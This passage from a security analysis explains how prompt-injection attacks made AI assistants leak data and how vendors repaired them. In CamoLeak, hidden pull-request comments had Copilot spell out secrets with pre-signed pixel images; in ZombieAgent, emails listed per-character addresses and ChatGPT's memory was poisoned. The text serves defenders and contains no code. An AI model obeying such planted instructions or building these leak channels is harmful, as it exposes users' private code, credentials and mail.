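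GitHub's image proxy, Camo, used signed addresses like those described in the previous section, so Copilot Chat could not produce a working address with stolen text in it. Legit Security's *CamoLeak* explains how a researcher got around this in June 2025. GitHub will sign the address of an outside image for anyone who submits a document containing that address, so the researcher had GitHub sign a separate address for every letter and symbol in advance.

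The researcher put this alphabet in a hidden comment in the description of a pull request, a proposed change to a project's code. When someone asked Copilot Chat about the pull request, it followed instructions in the comment to play a game and draw some text using the images. Each image was a single transparent pixel, so the user saw nothing. Copilot had the same access rights as the person asking, so the attack could reach that person's private projects. In one test, Copilot spelled out an unpublished security flaw from a private project. In another, it searched the victim's code for a cloud access key and leaked the result.

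Caching would have hidden repeated requests for the same letter, so the researcher told Copilot to add a random number to the end of each address, and Camo accepted the altered addresses. Rejecting such additions would not have stopped the attack, since an attacker can get several addresses signed for each letter.

GitHub had turned off images in Copilot Chat by August 14, 2025, which fixed the flaw. Press coverage collected in OECD's *GitHub Copilot Chat Vulnerability Exposes Private Code and Secrets* (2025) dates the disclosure to October 8.

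OpenAI's rule in late 2025 failed for the same reason. In *ShadowLeak* (2025), the security company Radware described an attack it had found on ChatGPT's connection to Gmail, in which private data left directly from OpenAI's servers. OpenAI responded by allowing ChatGPT to open web addresses only exactly as it received them. In Radware's *ZombieAgent*, the attacker's email listed a ready-made address for each letter and digit, plus one for a space. ChatGPT opened them one at a time to spell out what it had found in the inbox.

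Requests can arrive out of order, so Radware also made a separate address for each character in each position, which means no address repeats. Covering 26 letters and ten digits over b positions takes 36b addresses, or 360 for a block of ten characters. A six-digit login code needs only 60.

Limiting the number of requests only partly protects against this, because the attacker can supply more addresses to choose from. If each request has its own set of m addresses, k requests can distinguish mᵏ messages, and the attacker supplies km addresses in total. The table shows what a six-digit code requires.

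| Requests allowed | Addresses for each request | Addresses in the email |
|---|---|---|
| 6 | 10 | 60 |
| 3 | 100 | 300 |
| 2 | 1,000 | 2,000 |
| 1 | 1,000,000 | 1,000,000 |

At 40 characters each, 2,000 addresses take up 80,000 characters, which is long for an email but well within what current models can read. A million addresses would take up 40 million characters, which is too long, so a limit of one request protects the code. That one request could still reveal which of 1,000 companies the user's employer plans to buy. Two controls from the previous section, opening only addresses that the user supplied and downloading everything when the email arrives, are stronger because they don't let the model choose which address to open.

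ZombieAgent also found an ordering mistake in how OpenAI protected ChatGPT's memory. ChatGPT could not use memory after using Gmail or another connected service in the same conversation, but it could read memory first and use Gmail afterwards. An attacker could therefore get a victim to upload a file that made ChatGPT save a rule in memory to read a particular email and follow its instructions before answering any message. In another version, ChatGPT leaked addresses from the inbox, and the attacker's server sent the same malicious email to each address.

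Radware reported the flaws on September 26, 2025, and OpenAI fixed them on December 16. ChatGPT now refuses to open links from emails, except well-known public ones, according to Particle.news' *Radware’s ‘ZombieAgent’ Bypasses ChatGPT Fixes, Forcing New OpenAI Restrictions*. This fits the public-index rule in the previous section.

### Cato's charge of too little progress

Cato's researchers concluded that Microsoft had made "too little progress" since EchoLeak, Infosecurity Magazine reports. Cato sells security products for AI systems, so it has an interest in that conclusion, but much of the evidence supports it. A permitted Microsoft service passed stolen data to an outside server in attacks in June 2025 and June 2026, and again in ReLeak. Prompts in links worked in the enterprise search page after Microsoft had patched that flaw in the consumer product.

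Microsoft received the ReLeak reports between July 29 and August 20 and took between four weeks and about three and a half months to release the three patches. EchoLeak took about four months to patch, and CoSnitch took eight. Infosecurity Magazine described Microsoft's response as prompt. The charge is fair about how Microsoft deals with the underlying pattern, but less fair about how it handles individual reports. Copilot also gained new abilities in the meantime, such as running code, and two of the three ReLeak attacks used features other than the chat page.

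Nobody has reported a real theft through any of these attacks on Microsoft's products. The evidence that no customers were affected is stronger for EchoLeak than for ReLeak. Microsoft confirmed that EchoLeak had affected no customers, and it was in a good position to check because its own Teams servers would have made the outgoing requests. Cato said it knew of no customers affected by ReLeak, but it can't see Microsoft's logs. The OECD's database classes CamoLeak as an incident that caused harm, although Legit Security describes only its own tests.

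### Repairs and lessons

| Attack | Assumption that failed | Repair |
|---|---|---|
| EchoLeak | Injections address an AI; links have one form; permitted hosts don't pass requests on | Microsoft changed its servers in May 2025 and now removes reference-style links and images from outside content |
| CamoLeak | A signed address can't carry private data | GitHub turned off images in Copilot Chat in August 2025 |
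| ZombieAgent | An unaltered address can't carry private data | OpenAI restricted links from emails in December 2025 |
| Reprompt | Checking the first request is enough | Microsoft patched it in January 2026 |
| SearchLeak | The browser waits for the finished answer; Bing doesn't pass requests on | Microsoft patched it in June 2026 |
| CoSnitch | A prompt in a link waits for the user | Microsoft patched it in August 2026 |
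| ReLeak | Permitted hosts, saved files and the code sandbox don't contact outside servers | Microsoft released three patches between September and November 2026 |

Varonis also advises defenders to check what each permitted host will fetch. Relevant services include link previews, image searches and tools for embedding other pages. Microsoft's list was hard to check because many entries had wildcards, such as `*.bing.com`, which permits any service on a Bing subdomain, including ones added later. A company can keep the pictures its assistant needs on a separate host that only serves stored files. If that isn't practical, a CSP can permit a single path on a host, although browsers ignore the path after a redirect.

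Developers should test each control with the others switched off. The EchoLeak researchers could get an outside image into Copilot's answer before they had any way past the CSP. That fault is worth fixing even if the browser blocks the request. A team that tests only the whole product sees the image fail to load and may conclude that the link filter works.

The recorder test already covers streamed answers, but repeated requests need a separate test. Taler recommends applying safeguards to repeated and follow-up requests as well as the first, and a tester can check this by asking for the same fetch twice.

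A product can also keep outsiders' text away from private data, which protects against leaks through channels that nobody has found yet. Copilot, for example, could leave emails from unknown senders out of the context whenever an answer draws on internal files. The *EchoLeak* analysis proposes this kind of separation, even though Copilot would then miss some relevant information. An employee who asks what a new supplier has offered would have to open the supplier's email or choose to include it.
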